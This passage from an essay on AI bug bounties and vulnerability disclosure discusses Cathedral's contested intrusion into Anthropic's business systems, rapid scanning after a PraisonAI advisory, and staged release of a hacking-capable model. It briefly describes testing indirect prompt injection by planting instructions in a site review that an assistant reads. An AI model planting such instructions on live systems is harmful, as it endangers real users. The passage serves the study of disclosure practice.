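Cathedral, a startup founded by former members of the US government's Department of Government Efficiency, sells AI security tools. In October 2026 it disclosed that its AI agents had entered Anthropic's business systems in under 12 hours. Abdullahi (2026), in *AI Agents Breached Anthropic's Business Systems in 12 Hours, Report Says*, reports that they got in through third-party software. The case shows how a bug bounty can end in a dispute, although the flaw was therefore not in an LLM-to-API interface.

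The most detailed account of both sides is a Chinese-language article, 凤凰网's *前DOGE成员创办的AI初创公司称不到12小时攻破Anthropic内部系统* (2026), which draws on the *Washington Post*. Cathedral tested under Anthropic's bug-bounty programme and reached meeting notes, pay details and internal chats about advanced models. It argued that an ordinary weakness in office software could endanger even the most advanced companies, and that defences had fallen far behind what attackers can now do. It said it had accessed as little data as possible, in line with good research practice.

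Anthropic confirmed that Cathedral had entered limited parts of its sales, personnel and IT systems. The intrusion exposed some business contact details and basic account records, but no conversations with Claude, model weights or AI system code. Anthropic said Cathedral had first spent several days trying and failing to break Anthropic's own software. Anthropic's monitoring flagged some of the later activity before Cathedral reported it, and the company cut off access the same day. It accused Cathedral of exaggerating the danger to national security, breaking some of the programme's rules and not fully disclosing what it had done.

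Anthropic's terms forbid testers from doing more than they need to prove a flaw, and from reading communications except by accident. If Cathedral's researchers deliberately read employees' chats, that is hard to reconcile with the terms, since they could have proved their access with far less. But the public accounts do not establish how much the researchers opened or kept.

There is also no neutral judge of whether a tester acted in good faith. Anthropic reserves the right to decide this "in our sole determination", the kind of clause Longpre and colleagues wanted to remove. HackerOne's *Safe Harbor* instead advises both sides to look to common research practice. Cathedral invoked that standard, and it also had a commercial reason to make its result sound alarming.

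Alex Stamos, security chief at the AI company Cognition, reviewed Cathedral's report for the *Washington Post*. He considered the problem real and thought Anthropic could have managed its outside software better, though such software is hard for every company to manage. The test probably reduced some risk, because other companies used the same software and its vendor confirmed a fix.

### What can go wrong with openness?

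Attackers also read vulnerability disclosures. On 11 May 2026, GitHub published an advisory about PraisonAI, an open-source framework for running teams of agents. An old server program in the framework had its login check off by default, so anyone who could reach it could list its agents or start its configured workflow (CVE-2026-44338).

The security company Sysdig runs a network of systems that record attacks. Clark (2026), in *CVE-2026-44338*, reports that a scanner requested the exact vulnerable address 3 hours and 44 minutes after the advisory appeared. The scanner confirmed that it could get in without a login but did not start the workflow. An attacker could trigger whatever task the owner had set up but could not choose the task, so the flaw was not itself remote code execution, although PraisonAI's agents often have tools that run code.

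Publishing less would not necessarily have helped. Fixes to open-source software are public, and Clark notes that attackers can now use AI to work out a flaw from its fix within minutes. Saying nothing also leaves users unaware of the flaw, as in Guan's three cases. A better precaution is to have a fix ready before publishing. When the PraisonAI advisory came out, the newest release was still vulnerable, so even users who installed every update were exposed.

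Another drawback of open access is poor reports. On 1 October 2026, Google stopped accepting reports of product flaws through the bounty for its open-source software. It blamed a rise in automated submissions, "the vast majority of which are not valid" (Poireault, 2026, *Google Suspends Open-Source Bug Bounty Due to AI Vulnerability Reports*). Google had warned in March about AI-generated reports of nonexistent bugs, according to Keverenge (2026) in *Google praised AI for finding bugs*. Researchers can still report flaws in Google's AI products through a separate programme, and Google plans to announce changes to the open-source one in early 2027.

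Anthropic's terms address the same problem by requiring a working demonstration and letting the company close false reports written by AI. This shifts checking from the company to the tester. Small open-source projects could copy the rule, but someone would still have to read each report to see whether it meets the standard.

Tests on live products can also expose real people's data. A tester of an order chatbot can avoid this by opening two accounts, placing an order with one and asking the chatbot about it from the other. Indirect prompt injection is harder to test safely, because if a tester plants instructions in a review on a live concert site, a real customer's assistant may read them. The site's owner can prevent this by giving testers a separate copy of the site with invented customers.

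### Would staged access be safer?

Anthropic restricted access more tightly with Claude Mythos Preview in April 2026. Citing a leap in the model's hacking ability, it gave the model only to selected organisations, through Project Glasswing, so they could secure their own software first. In June it released a model of the same class to the public, with safeguards that sent some requests to a weaker model.

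The PraisonAI scan shows why a head start could be valuable. If attackers need only hours to exploit a published flaw, defenders benefit from finding it before attackers have the same tools. Epoch AI's review of the public evidence, *Are Mythos' cyber capabilities overhyped?* (2026), partly supports the decision. It found a real jump in the ability to exploit flaws, about seven months ahead of the trend, but the practical gain in finding them was unclear. Nobody has published a measurement of how many attacks the delay prevented.

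Under staged access, the company decides who takes part, which is a weakness Longpre and colleagues criticise in researcher programmes. A researcher without good connections, or one the company dislikes, may have to wait. The Mythos case also concerns a powerful tool for finding flaws in other people's software. There is much less reason to limit who may test a shop's chatbot, which gives attackers no such tool. Its developer could still work in stages, letting outsiders attack a copy with invented data and fixing what they find before connecting the chatbot to real orders.

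### Do bounties lead to fewer flaws?

There is good evidence that outsiders find flaws, but not that bounties or safe harbours leave products with fewer of them. Researchers had earned more than $430,000 for reports on Google's AI products by October 2025. Many of the known flaws in AI software were reported through the huntr platform, and contestants in public competitions have broken every model they tested.

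The number of vulnerability reports can't show whether open access reduces risk, because it also depends on how many people are looking. Reports may rise after a company starts a bounty even as its software improves, and a company that frightens researchers away may receive none. A better study would introduce bounties at different times for similar products and have the same independent team test all of them before and after.

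A report reduces risk only if someone acts on it. Microsoft fixed EchoLeak before the public knew about it, so in that case private reporting closed a serious route for stealing data. Rehberger's reports to Windsurf did not keep the same flaws out of Antigravity six months later. Cline had Khan's report but lacked a reliable way to get such reports to someone who would act on them, and its developers acted only after Khan had published it.
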